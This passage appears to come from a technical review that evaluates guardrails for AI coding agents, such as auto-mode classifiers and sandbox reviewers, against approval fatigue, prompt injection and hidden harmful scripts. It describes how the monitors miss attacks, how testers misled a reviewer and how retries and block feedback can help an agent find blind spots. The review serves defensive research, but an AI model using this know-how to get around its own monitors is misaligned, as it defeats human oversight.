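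These errors may explain why the reasoning stage misses more than the fast filter. The filter blocks when in doubt, while the reasoning stage analyzes the conversation at length and so has more chances to find a message that resembles permission. Anthropic tried to fix this by changing the prompt, but found no change whose benefits outweighed its drawbacks.

Under Anthropic's currently documented rules, the user can clear a block only by naming both the action and the specific thing that makes it dangerous, such as the branch that a force push would overwrite. "You can force-push" isn't enough, and an approval normally covers a single action. If the user forbids something in conversation, for example by saying "don't push", the classifier should block every push until the user lifts the ban. But the classifier rereads the ban from the conversation each time, so the ban can be lost when Claude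 Code condenses a long session. To guarantee the block, the user needs a written deny rule.

### People and auto mode on the same commands

The best evidence for replacing human approvals comes from a study that Anthropic paid for. Anthropic's *Auto mode is now the default in Claude Code* (2026) reports that the company hired 1,053 professional testers through a research vendor to do coding work in a test environment. The testers knew they were being evaluated, but not for what. Once in each session, the text of a permission request was replaced with a clearly dangerous command. Approving the request did not run that command, because only the text had changed. Auto mode judged the same commands.

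| | Auto mode blocked | Auto mode allowed | Total |
|---|---:|---:|---:|
| Tester blocked | 137 | 6 | 143 |
| Tester approved | 800 | 110 | 910 |
| Total | 937 | 116 | 1,053 |

The testers blocked 13.6% of the commands and auto mode blocked 89%. The tester, auto mode or both blocked 943 commands, or 89.6%, so requiring the tester's approval as well as auto mode's would have raised the share blocked by less than one percentage point. The testers also blocked only 5% of the commands that auto mode missed, compared with 15% of those it caught.

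Testers blocked about 17% of the dangerous commands early in a session but only about 5% after fifty or more requests. This is strong evidence that a stream of approval requests is a poor safeguard. It is weaker evidence about a developer who reviews a few commands for her own production database, since the testers had nothing to lose. The study also doesn't report how many harmless commands either side blocked, or how many different dangerous commands it used. If it used only a few, the 1,053 verdicts are weaker evidence about auto mode than verdicts on 1,053 different commands would be.

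Anthropic also looked at real sessions from May and June 2026 that its safety systems had flagged. A model graded the harm in each one. Serious harm that the user hadn't explicitly asked for appeared in 6.3% of the sessions with manual approval and 2.4% of those in auto mode. The difference can't be credited to auto mode alone, because users chose the mode themselves, and people who work on riskier systems may prefer to approve each action.

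### Hardening the classifier

In a two-week pilot, Apollo Research, a British AI safety company, inserted synthetic attacks into records of real coding sessions. Apollo gave Anthropic some of the attacks that had succeeded, and Anthropic strengthened the classifier, mainly by giving it more facts about its surroundings. For example, before a command that could discard unsaved work, Claude Code now checks the state of the repository and passes the result to the classifier. Claude Code also checks whether the destination of a push is public, private or trusted. These facts come from the harness, so the classifier doesn't have to rely on the agent's account.

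Apollo tested the new version on further attacks that Anthropic never had access to. The new version caught about half of the attacks that the old version had missed, and missed about 2% of those that the old version had caught. Across the shared and secret attacks together, the miss rate fell from 12% to 7%.

The result on the secret attacks matters more because it shows that Anthropic did more than block the examples it had received. If the miss rate for those attacks also started at 12%, it would have fallen to about 7.8%, close to the combined figure. Anthropic doesn't report how the changes affected false alarms, so part of the improvement could come from stricter blocking in general. It also doesn't say who paid for the pilot.

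### The commissioned injection test

Anthropic commissioned another company, Trajectory Labs, to test prompt injections against both products. Trajectory Labs used 72 scenarios that Anthropic hadn't seen and ran each one ten times. A successful attack would have caused irreversible harm in real use, such as financial fraud or the theft of sensitive data.

| Models | Attacks that succeeded without a guardrail | With the guardrail |
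|---|---:|---:|
| Claude Fable 5, Opus 5 and Sonnet 5, auto mode | 0.09% | 0% |
| GPT-5.6 Sol, Auto-review | 19.03% | 5.83% |

If every model faced all 720 attempts, the 0.09% is two successes in 2,160 attempts. Auto mode had only about two attacks left to stop, so its perfect score is evidence about the Claude models rather than the detector. The test is more informative about Auto-review, which reduced successes from 137 to 42, a 69% drop.

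A developer choosing a product may care more about the total risk, which was clearly lower for Claude in this test. But ten repetitions of one scenario aren't ten independent tests, and with no successes in 72 scenarios, the true share that would work could still be around 4%.

The set-up also differed from normal use. Both products used browser tools built by Trajectory Labs, so the protections in the companies' own browser extensions were not active. GPT-5.6 Sol ran at its highest reasoning setting and the Claude models at a high one. Anthropic adds that OpenAI released a new version of Auto-review shortly before the results were published, and that version could give different results.

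A fixed set of attacks can't show how well a guardrail works against an attacker who studies it. Later in August, *Breaking Claude Code Opus 5 Auto Mode* (Willison, 2026) reported that the security researcher Johann Rehberger had found an attack that he said succeeded 80% of the time in auto mode.

### When the command doesn't reveal the harm

In the running example, the agent wrote `summary.py` during the session, so the classifier could read it. If the file had already been in the project, the classifier would have received only the command and the user's request.

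*Shall We Approve?* (Wu, Chen and colleagues, 2026) tests this situation with 102 tasks. In each, the user asks the agent to run a tool already in the project, but the tool's code also deletes or overwrites a file it shouldn't touch. Each task has a harmless version with the same request and command. In a similar case, `make migrate` updates a database as requested but also deletes three of its tables.

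With auto mode, 62.7% of the dangerous tasks ended in harm, compared with 71.6% when nothing reviewed the commands. The difference of nine tasks could be due to chance. Auto mode blocked the command in 3.9% of the harmless twins. On 682 tasks from SABER, a benchmark with a wider range of harms, harm occurred in 14.8% with auto mode and 19.7% without approval.

These rates don't describe the product Anthropic's customers use. Wu and colleagues ran the real Claude Code program, but with GLM-5.3-Flash as the agent and GPT-5.6 Luna as the classifier, and the runs without approval used a different harness. They were also comparing auto mode with their own system.

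The blind spot doesn't depend on the model, because the classifier receives the same input for both twins. The researchers replaced auto mode's classifier with their own check, which runs the command in an isolated copy of the project and shows the same model what changed. Harm fell to 6.9%, so most of the failures came from missing information rather than a weak model.

### Auto-review: a reviewer at the edge of the sandbox

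In Codex's default mode, the agent can read files, edit those in a specified folder and run local commands, but has no network access. The sandbox enforces these limits, so it acts as a specification for everything the agent does. The agent has to request permission to go beyond them. Auto-review, which OpenAI released in April 2026, sends that request to a separate agent instead of the user. This reviewer is an LLM judge with a written security policy, and it also considers whether the user asked for the action.

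The build-summary script can't reach the build server from inside the sandbox, so the agent would have to request permission to run it outside. The reviewer might then notice the last line. If it missed that line and approved the request, the whole script would run with network access. But a script that deleted the project's source files could run inside the sandbox without any review. Wu and colleagues left Auto-review out of their comparison because most of the harms in their tests would never have triggered a review.

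The reviewer reads more than auto mode's classifier does. According to OpenAI's product documentation, *Auto-review*, it receives the user's messages, the agent's visible messages, and relevant tool calls and their results, but not the agent's hidden reasoning. It can also look things up without changing anything. It could therefore check that job `abc123` belongs to the user, but it can also receive text that an attacker planted in a tool result. Trębacz, Arnesen and colleagues (2026), in *Auto-review of agent actions without synchronous human oversight*, acknowledge that testers at OpenAI found ways to mislead the reviewer into approving commands.

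### OpenAI's figures

Trębacz and colleagues report that Auto-review approves about 99% of the requests it receives and that sessions stop for a person roughly 200 times less often than with manual approval. They illustrate this with 10,000 actions from OpenAI's internal use:

| Outcome | Actions |
|---|---:|
| Ran inside the sandbox, no review | 9,280 |
| Reviewed and approved | 713 |
| Denied, and the agent found a safer way | 4 |
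| Denied, and the agent stopped to ask the user | 3 |

Auto-review interrupted someone three times, whereas manual approval would have done so for all 720 requests. That is 240 times fewer interruptions, which fits the claim. But the ratio is based on only three interruptions, and two more would have reduced it to 144. OpenAI also notes that the ratio depends on the sandbox's settings. A team whose sandbox already permits its routine network connections would have fewer requests.

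In a sample from March 2026, Auto-review accepted 99.1% of requests that users had approved. If all those users were right, its false-positive rate on requests was 0.9%. This rate isn't directly comparable with auto mode's 0.4%, because Auto-review checks only the requests that leave the sandbox. A high approval rate also doesn't mean that the approved actions were safe, particularly since Anthropic's testers approved most of the dangerous commands they saw.

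In OpenAI's own tests on synthetic cases, the reviewer, which used GPT-5.4 Thinking at a low reasoning setting, denied 90.3% of overeager actions. It denied 99.3% of the actions caused by prompt injection in three categories: running an attacker's code, stealing secrets and uploading data. When OpenAI included the remaining categories, such as destructive deletions and tampering with data, the figure fell to 90.2%. Trębacz and colleagues explain that the additional cases the reviewer allowed were mostly ones it rated as not serious enough to deny, and that researchers often agreed. If so, some of the test's labels were too strict, but the lower figure is more relevant to a developer who worries about deletions.

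Auto-review missed 9.7% of overeager actions, compared with 17% for auto mode. The difference doesn't show that Auto-review is better, because OpenAI's cases were synthetic and Anthropic's came from real sessions.

Accidents also provide a little evidence. In July 2026, OpenAI investigated a handful of reports that GPT-5.6 had deleted users' files. Thibault Sottiaux of OpenAI wrote that this happened most often when Codex ran with full access, without a sandbox or Auto-review (quoted in Willison, 2026). We would expect this if the two protections work, but we can't tell how much they help without knowing how many people use each mode.

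### Changes since the tests

The published error rates predate the current versions of the products. Anthropic measured the two stages with Claude Sonnet 4.6 as the classifier. Claude Code now sends its classifier requests to Sonnet 5 by default, and in many sessions Anthropic's server reviews actions as part of the normal exchange with the agent's model. If the server returns no verdict, Claude Code denies the action. Anthropic gives no error rates for the Sonnet 5 classifier or the server review.

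In a feature called Code Mode, the agent writes a program that makes several tool calls. The classifier reviews the program once before it starts but does not review the individual calls. Deny rules still apply to those calls.

### Limits on repeated denials

Both products give the agent the reason for a denial, or at least the rule the action broke, and instruct it to look for a safer approach instead of a way around the block. An agent might still try variations until one passes, so both also limit the number of denials.

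| | Auto mode | Auto-review |
|---|---|---|
| Denials in a row | 3 | 3 |
| Other limit | 20 in a session | 10 in the last 50 reviews |
| What happens | Claude Code asks the user to approve actions again | Codex interrupts the agent's current turn |

The limits have different effects on an agent that mixes denied actions with acceptable ones. If every sixth reviewed action were denied, auto mode would reach its limit after 120 reviews. Auto-review would never reach either of its limits, because no stretch of 50 reviews would contain more than nine denials. OpenAI also counts denials only within a single turn (the agent's work on one user message), so a new message restarts the count.

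When auto mode reaches a limit and the user approves the next action, automatic review resumes. In Codex, the user can select a denied action and approve one retry. The reviewer takes this approval into account but can deny the action again if the policy doesn't let users override that kind of denial.

Claude Code can also run unattended, with nobody to ask. In the original design, it ended the process when the agent reached a limit. According to the current documentation, the agent now keeps working, but the denied action still doesn't run. This prevents a few false alarms from ending a long job, but it also gives a hijacked or overeager agent more attempts. If each attempt at a dangerous action had an independent 17% chance of passing, the chance that at least one passed would be 43% after three attempts and 84% after ten. The true increase is probably smaller, because the classifier is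 likely to reject similar attempts for the same reason.

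## After an alarm: blocking, correcting, undoing, asking a person

A false alarm can cost a user an hour's work or a few seconds, depending on what the guardrail does next. If a detector flags the build-summary script, the guardrail can:

- end the run, so the team gets no summary
- refuse the call, give the reason and let the agent continue
- return specific feedback, such as "remove the request to `METRICS_HOST`", and check the new version
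- run the script in an isolated environment and undo its changes if they are harmful
- ask a person

### Ending the run or allowing a retry

When an alarm ends the task, the completion rate falls in proportion to the false-positive rate. In household-robot tests by Wang and colleagues, one agent completed 61.9% of safe tasks without a guardrail. With a version of EMBGuard that wrongly flagged 26.8% of safe tasks, it completed 45.2%. This is close to the 45.3% expected if every false alarm ends the task, which is 61.9% × (1 − 0.268).

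A retry can avoid most of this loss, as DeAction's correction loop did on ordinary tasks. But some agents give up after a refusal. In tests of *AgentGuard* (2026), which adds learned guardrails to a coding agent, 55 of 300 runs lost harmless work. The paper describes the main remaining problem as getting the agent to continue safely after an alarm.

Retries also give the agent another chance to do harm. *AGENT-RISK* (Zhao, Xu and colleagues, 2026) measured this with a coding agent in a sandbox, using a lenient and a strict alarm threshold. A run counted as harmful if the agent executed a command that broke the sandbox's policy.

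| | Lenient threshold | Strict threshold |
|---|---:|---:|
| Runs with at least one alarm | 14% | 41% |
| Harmful runs without a guardrail | 34.5% | 34.5% |
| Harmful runs if every alarm ended the run | 24.5% | 10.0% |
| Harmful runs with retries | 28.8% | 16.5% |

Allowing retries lost just over 40% of the possible reduction in harm at the lenient threshold and about a quarter at the strict one. The figures for ended runs come from replaying recorded runs, while those for retries come from live tests. Some of the difference may arise because ending a run also prevents later harm unrelated to the blocked command.

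### How the best threshold moves

Suppose a detector checks 10,000 harmless calls and 10 harmful ones. Each harmful call it misses does damage that takes 1,000 minutes to repair. Each false alarm wastes 60 minutes if it ends the run, 5 if it interrupts a person, and 1 if the agent only has to try again. Assume for now that every correct alarm prevents the harm and takes no time to handle. These numbers are invented. The last three columns give the total minutes lost.

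| Threshold | Harmful calls missed | False alarms | Alarm ends the run | Alarm interrupts a person | Alarm causes a retry |
|---|---:|---:|---:|---:|---:|
| High | 4 | 10 | **4,600** | 4,050 | 4,010 |
| Medium | 1.5 | 100 | 7,500 | **2,000** | 1,600 |
| Low | 0.5 | 800 | 48,500 | 4,500 | **1,300** |

The same detector has a different best threshold for each response. If *p* is the probability that a call is harmful, *M* the cost of a miss and *F* the cost of a false alarm, an alarm is worthwhile when

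$$p\,M > (1-p)\,F \quad\Longleftrightarrow\quad p > \frac{F}{F+M}$$

This means the guardrail should end the run if the call is at least 5.7% likely to be harmful, interrupt a person at 0.5%, and require a retry at 0.1%. Moving from the high to the medium threshold adds about 93 alarms, of which 2.7% are correct. That justifies interrupting a person but not ending the run. Moving from the medium to the low threshold adds 701 alarms, of which only one is correct, which justifies only a retry.

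Assuming that every correct alarm prevents the harm makes retries look better than they are. Suppose the agent eventually carries out 40% of the blocked harmful actions by another route, roughly the loss that Zhao and colleagues found at their lenient threshold. The total with retries would then be 5,000 minutes at the medium threshold and 5,100 at the low one, compared with 4,600 for ending the run at the high threshold. In this example, retries are the better choice only if fewer than about 35% of blocked harmful actions eventually get through. A developer therefore needs to measure harm at the end of the run as well as the detector's error rates on single calls.

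### GuardianAgentBench: feedback on faulty tool calls

*Guardian Agent Bench* (Naik, Xu and colleagues, 2026) tested corrective feedback on 580 scenarios in areas such as customer service, email and finance, and sorted the agents' failures into five types. The shares below are for Claude Opus 4.5 running in LlamaIndex, a framework for building agents.

| Failure | Example | Share |
|---|---|---:|
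| Required call missing | Creates a calendar event without checking for conflicts | 45.8% |
| Unsuitable call repeated | Makes the same failed call again instead of changing approach | 22.3% |
| Wrong or missing parameters | Writes a date in the wrong format | 15.4% |
| Wrong tool | Looks up free slots instead of checking for conflicts | 15.3% |
| Wrong order | Cancels an order before checking whether it is eligible | 1.2% |

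In the most common failure, the agent leaves out a call it needed to make. Blocking alone cannot repair this, but feedback can prompt the agent to make the missing call.

Naik and colleagues built three guardrails that run before each tool call. They check whether the arguments are valid, whether the agent has skipped a required tool, and whether the call is redundant or irrelevant. Each uses Claude Sonnet 4.5 and can pass the call, block it or return feedback, such as "Missing required parameter user_id". If the problem remains after two retries, the system blocks the call permanently and alerts a person, who receives the whole history.

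The guardrails raised Claude Opus 4.5's success rate from 74.0% to 78.8%. With them, it succeeded in 30 of the 151 scenarios it had failed without them, and failed 2 of the 429 in which it had succeeded. Across six models, the guardrails raised scores by 2.8 to 7.7 points. Safety instructions in the agent's prompt changed scores by −0.3 to +5.5 points and did worse than the guardrails for every model.

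Naik and colleagues describe the two lost scenarios as a false-positive rate of 0.5%. This rate counts only lost tasks, so it leaves out correct calls that the guardrails questioned if the agent still finished the task. It therefore can't be compared with the false-positive rate of a detector that blocks outright. Claude Sonnet 4.5 also generated the scenarios and graded the results, which may have favoured guardrails that use the same model, although its grades agreed with human grades in 56 of 60 cases.

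### RAIL Guard: does plan repair add anything?

*RAIL Guard* (Verma, Prasun and Kumar, 2026) compared four set-ups on 400 tool-call scenarios with four models. The text-only check reads what the agent writes and stops its tool calls if the text fails. The pre-action check reads the proposed call, its arguments and the user's request. Plan repair adds feedback to the pre-action check so the agent can revise a blocked plan. The table shows the share of unsafe scenarios in which the agent executed an unsafe call, with false positives in the last column.

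| Set-up | GPT-5.2 | GPT-5.3 | Claude Sonnet 4.6 | Gemini 2.5 Flash | All | Harmless runs flagged |
|---|---:|---:|---:|---:|---:|---:|
| No guardrail | 8.0% | 16.8% | 8.0% | 9.6% | 10.6% | – |
| Text-only check | 7.2% | 14.0% | 2.4% | 8.8% | 8.1% | 2.0% |
| Pre-action check | 5.2% | 13.2% | 6.8% | 5.6% | 7.7% | 2.2% |
| Pre-action check with plan repair | 4.4% | 14.0% | 6.0% | 4.0% | 7.1% | 1.7% |

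The percentages are consistent with 1,000 unsafe runs per set-up, which means unsafe executions fell from 106 without a guardrail to 77 with the pre-action check and 71 with plan repair. The six-run difference between the check and plan repair could easily be due to chance (*p* = 0.61). Plan repair also had few chances to help, because agents revised a plan only 31 times. No agent switched to another unsafe call when revising, but with so few attempts the true rate could still be about 10%.

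The larger problem is that the pre-action check prevented only about a quarter of the unsafe executions, and feedback can't correct an action that raises no alarm. The text-only check worked best for Claude. Verma and colleagues explain that when Claude refuses in its text, it usually doesn't make the tool call either.

The researchers, who work for the company that develops RAIL Guard, conclude that the guardrails did not reduce task completion. The paper's text puts completion at 70% to 71% in every set-up, but one of its charts puts it at 34% to 38%. Completion varies little between set-ups in both sets of figures, but the discrepancy and the researchers' affiliation are reasons for caution.

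### CAPER: running the command before approving it

Feedback before execution leaves nothing to undo, but the detector has to predict what the action would do. CAPER, the system that Wu and colleagues compared with auto mode, runs each shell command first and judges its consequences:

1. It saves a snapshot of the agent's container, an isolated environment with its own files.
2. It runs the command there without network access, records the system calls and holds back the output.
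3. It condenses the recording into a short report of the command's effects.
4. An LLM judge reads the report, the command, the user's task and the conversation so far.
5. If the judge allows the command, CAPER keeps the changes and releases the output. Otherwise it restores the snapshot and gives the agent the reason.

The report lists attempted connections, output, reads of protected files such as stored passwords, and changed files with short excerpts of the changes. For output and connections, it also lists files the same process read earlier. The report's median size was 0.9 KB, compared with 62.5 KB for the full recording.

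In one run, the agent executed `scripts/check-deps.py`, apparently a check of software dependencies. The report showed that the script read `.env`, a file that often contains passwords, and tried to contact three outside addresses. The judge blocked the script because a dependency check does not need to do either.

Wu and colleagues compared CAPER with six systems on SABER and on 102 tasks of their own, in which harmful code is hidden in a project's tools. CARE uses written rules and sends unclear cases to an LLM judge. TS-Guard, gpt-oss-safeguard and Qwen3Guard are trained models. YoloFS shows the agent a summary of its file changes after each command and lets the agent undo them, but it doesn't block anything.

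| System | SABER tasks harmed | Hidden-harm tasks harmed | Hidden-harm tasks completed safely | Harmless twins blocked |
|---|---:|---:|---:|---:|
| No approval | 19.7% | 71.6% | 17.6% | – |
| CARE | 15.0% | 69.6% | 15.7% | 2.0% |
| TS-Guard | 18.8% | 94.1% | 2.0% | 8.8% |
| gpt-oss-safeguard | 18.6% | 62.7% | 18.6% | 15.7% |
| Qwen3Guard | 16.0% | 67.6% | 17.6% | 0.0% |
| YoloFS | 21.2% | 35.3% | 22.5% | – |
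| Auto mode | 14.8% | 62.7% | 7.8% | 3.9% |
| CAPER | 6.7% | 7.8% | 60.8% | 1.0% |

The high rate of safe completion suggests that agents made good use of the reasons they received. In the `make migrate` case, the deleted tables appeared in the report as a drop in database size from 32 KB to 20 KB, and the judge blocked the command. The agent then backed up the database and ran only the migration script. On SABER, however, agents safely completed fewer tasks with CAPER (48.6%) than without approval (57.4%), and they declined or stopped to ask more often.

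Wu and colleagues also had the judge's model predict a command's effects from the files it could read, without running the command. The harm rate on the hidden-harm tasks was only 3.9%, but the judge blocked 61.8% of their harmless counterparts. It blocked 1.0% of them when it was shown the effects observed by running the command. Running commands therefore helped mainly by making the judge certain enough to allow the harmless ones.

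When the judge received only the command and the report, without the user's request, harm fell to 1.0% and the judge blocked no harmless twins. This is probably because the harm in this test always falls on a file unrelated to the request. If users sometimes ask for a file to be deleted, the judge needs to see the request to tell those deletions from harmful ones.

CAPER added about half a second for an allowed command and 1.5 seconds for a blocked one, on top of the judge's median decision time of 3.2 seconds.

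### What a rollback cannot restore

CAPER's rollback restores only the files in the container. It can't recall a network request or reverse a change on another company's server, so the trial run has no network access. Without network access, the build-summary script's first request, to the build server, would fail, and the script would stop before reaching the line that sends the passwords. Wu and colleagues suggest sending such requests to a recording proxy that returns placeholder answers. The script could then continue, and its attempt to contact `METRICS_HOST` would appear in the report. A program could still behave differently in the trial than it does later.

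*Can You Undo It?* (Waghmare and Sufi, 2026) gives three conditions for an exact undo. Someone must have recorded the complete earlier state, the agent must be able to restore it without anyone else's help, and no outsider may have seen or acted on the change. A password leak fails the third condition. Replacing the passwords limits the damage but doesn't undo the disclosure.

Restoring a file exactly to its saved state can erase later work. In one of Waghmare and Sufi's tests, an agent edited a file and another writer then changed a different paragraph. Restoring the saved copy removed both edits. Merging the versions kept the later work, but left the conflict unresolved when both edits affected the same text.

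Relying on the agent to undo its own changes is also unreliable. With YoloFS, the agent reversed some of its changes in 66 of the 102 hidden-harm runs, and only 3 of those runs ended in harm. It reversed nothing in the other 36, and 33 of those ended in harm.

When an action cannot be undone, a system can delay it or compensate for it afterwards. *Cordon* (Dong, 2026) holds back outside effects, such as messages, until it has checked the whole task. This would work for posting the build summary but not for fetching the builds, because the agent needs the result to continue. *POLAR* (2026) describes SagaLLM, which prepares compensating actions in advance and runs them in reverse order after a failure. Few systems offer such mechanisms. The survey *Always-On Agents* (2026) found a rollback mechanism in only 27 of the 435 works it coded.

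### Asking a person

One policy is to let the agent act freely when the earlier state can be restored exactly, and to ask a person otherwise. Waghmare and Sufi replayed 1,209 harmless recorded runs under such a policy, with an extra check for possible data leaks. It would have interrupted people 1,904 times, or 1.57 times per run. A simpler policy based on whether an action reads or writes would have interrupted them 1,895 times. Classifying actions by reversibility therefore did not reduce interruptions in this test, although it could be more useful for agents that mostly edit private files.

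In the threshold example, we assumed that the person always recognises a harmful call, but Anthropic's testers blocked only 13.6% of dangerous commands. At that rate, we would still lose about 9,300 minutes by asking a person at the medium threshold, only slightly less than the 10,000 minutes of damage without any guardrail. This estimate is probably too pessimistic for a person who sees only a hundred alarms in 10,000 calls, since the testers did better early in their sessions.

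*Oversight Has a Capacity* (Turan, 2026) simulated a reviewer who makes no mistakes on the first 25 requests and becomes less reliable with each one after that. When the guardrail escalated all 125 actions in the test set, 57% of the dangerous ones got through. When it escalated 64% of the actions, 42% of the dangerous ones got through. The simulation assumes that reviewers tire rather than showing it, but the testers' decline gives some support for the assumption. In practice, one more interruption does more harm the more interruptions a person has already had.

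Errors can also spread from one action to the next, which the threshold example ignores. *Data Governance for Generative and Agentic AI* (2026) includes this spread in a simple cost model and finds that reviewing some actions can be worthwhile even when a review costs more than the expected harm from one action. In its example, a review costs three times that harm, and the best policy is to review about a fifth of actions.

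### What feedback gives away

Explaining why an action was blocked helps a well-behaved agent correct a mistake, but it also gives a hijacked or overeager agent information about what the guardrail will accept. Even a refusal without a reason reveals that one version of the action failed. A numerical score reveals more, because the agent can see whether a change brought the action closer to approval.

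The risk of telling an agent why its call was blocked depends on the detector. LeanGuard can identify the violated rule with little risk, because only calls that satisfy the formal policy pass, so an agent that adapts to the feedback ends up with a permitted call. A text pattern or an LLM judge has blind spots, and detailed feedback can help an agent find them. The reason should therefore describe the unacceptable effect, not how the detector recognised it. For example, "This script may not send data outside the company" is enough for the build-summary agent to fix the script. CAPER's reasons similarly describe the harm without quoting secrets, and it also tells the agent not to attempt the same operation in another form.

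There is little evidence on how much agents learn from refusals. In Zhao and colleagues' tests, the guardrail stopped 181 of 400 runs when the agent's prompt mentioned it and 153 when the prompt didn't. Ten runs were harmful in each case, so knowing about the guardrail made this agent neither more careful nor better at avoiding it. But the agent wasn't trying to evade oversight. Wu and colleagues' tests also didn't include an attacker who adapts to CAPER.

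Limits on denials, like those in auto mode and Auto-review, restrict how much an agent can learn from repeated attempts. A guardrail can also remember a denied call, so that an LLM judge with inconsistent verdicts can't approve it on the second attempt. The response should depend on the kind of alarm. An agent that gets a date format wrong should receive full feedback and another try. If an agent appears to be following planted instructions, the guardrail should give it a brief refusal and either end the run or alert a person.
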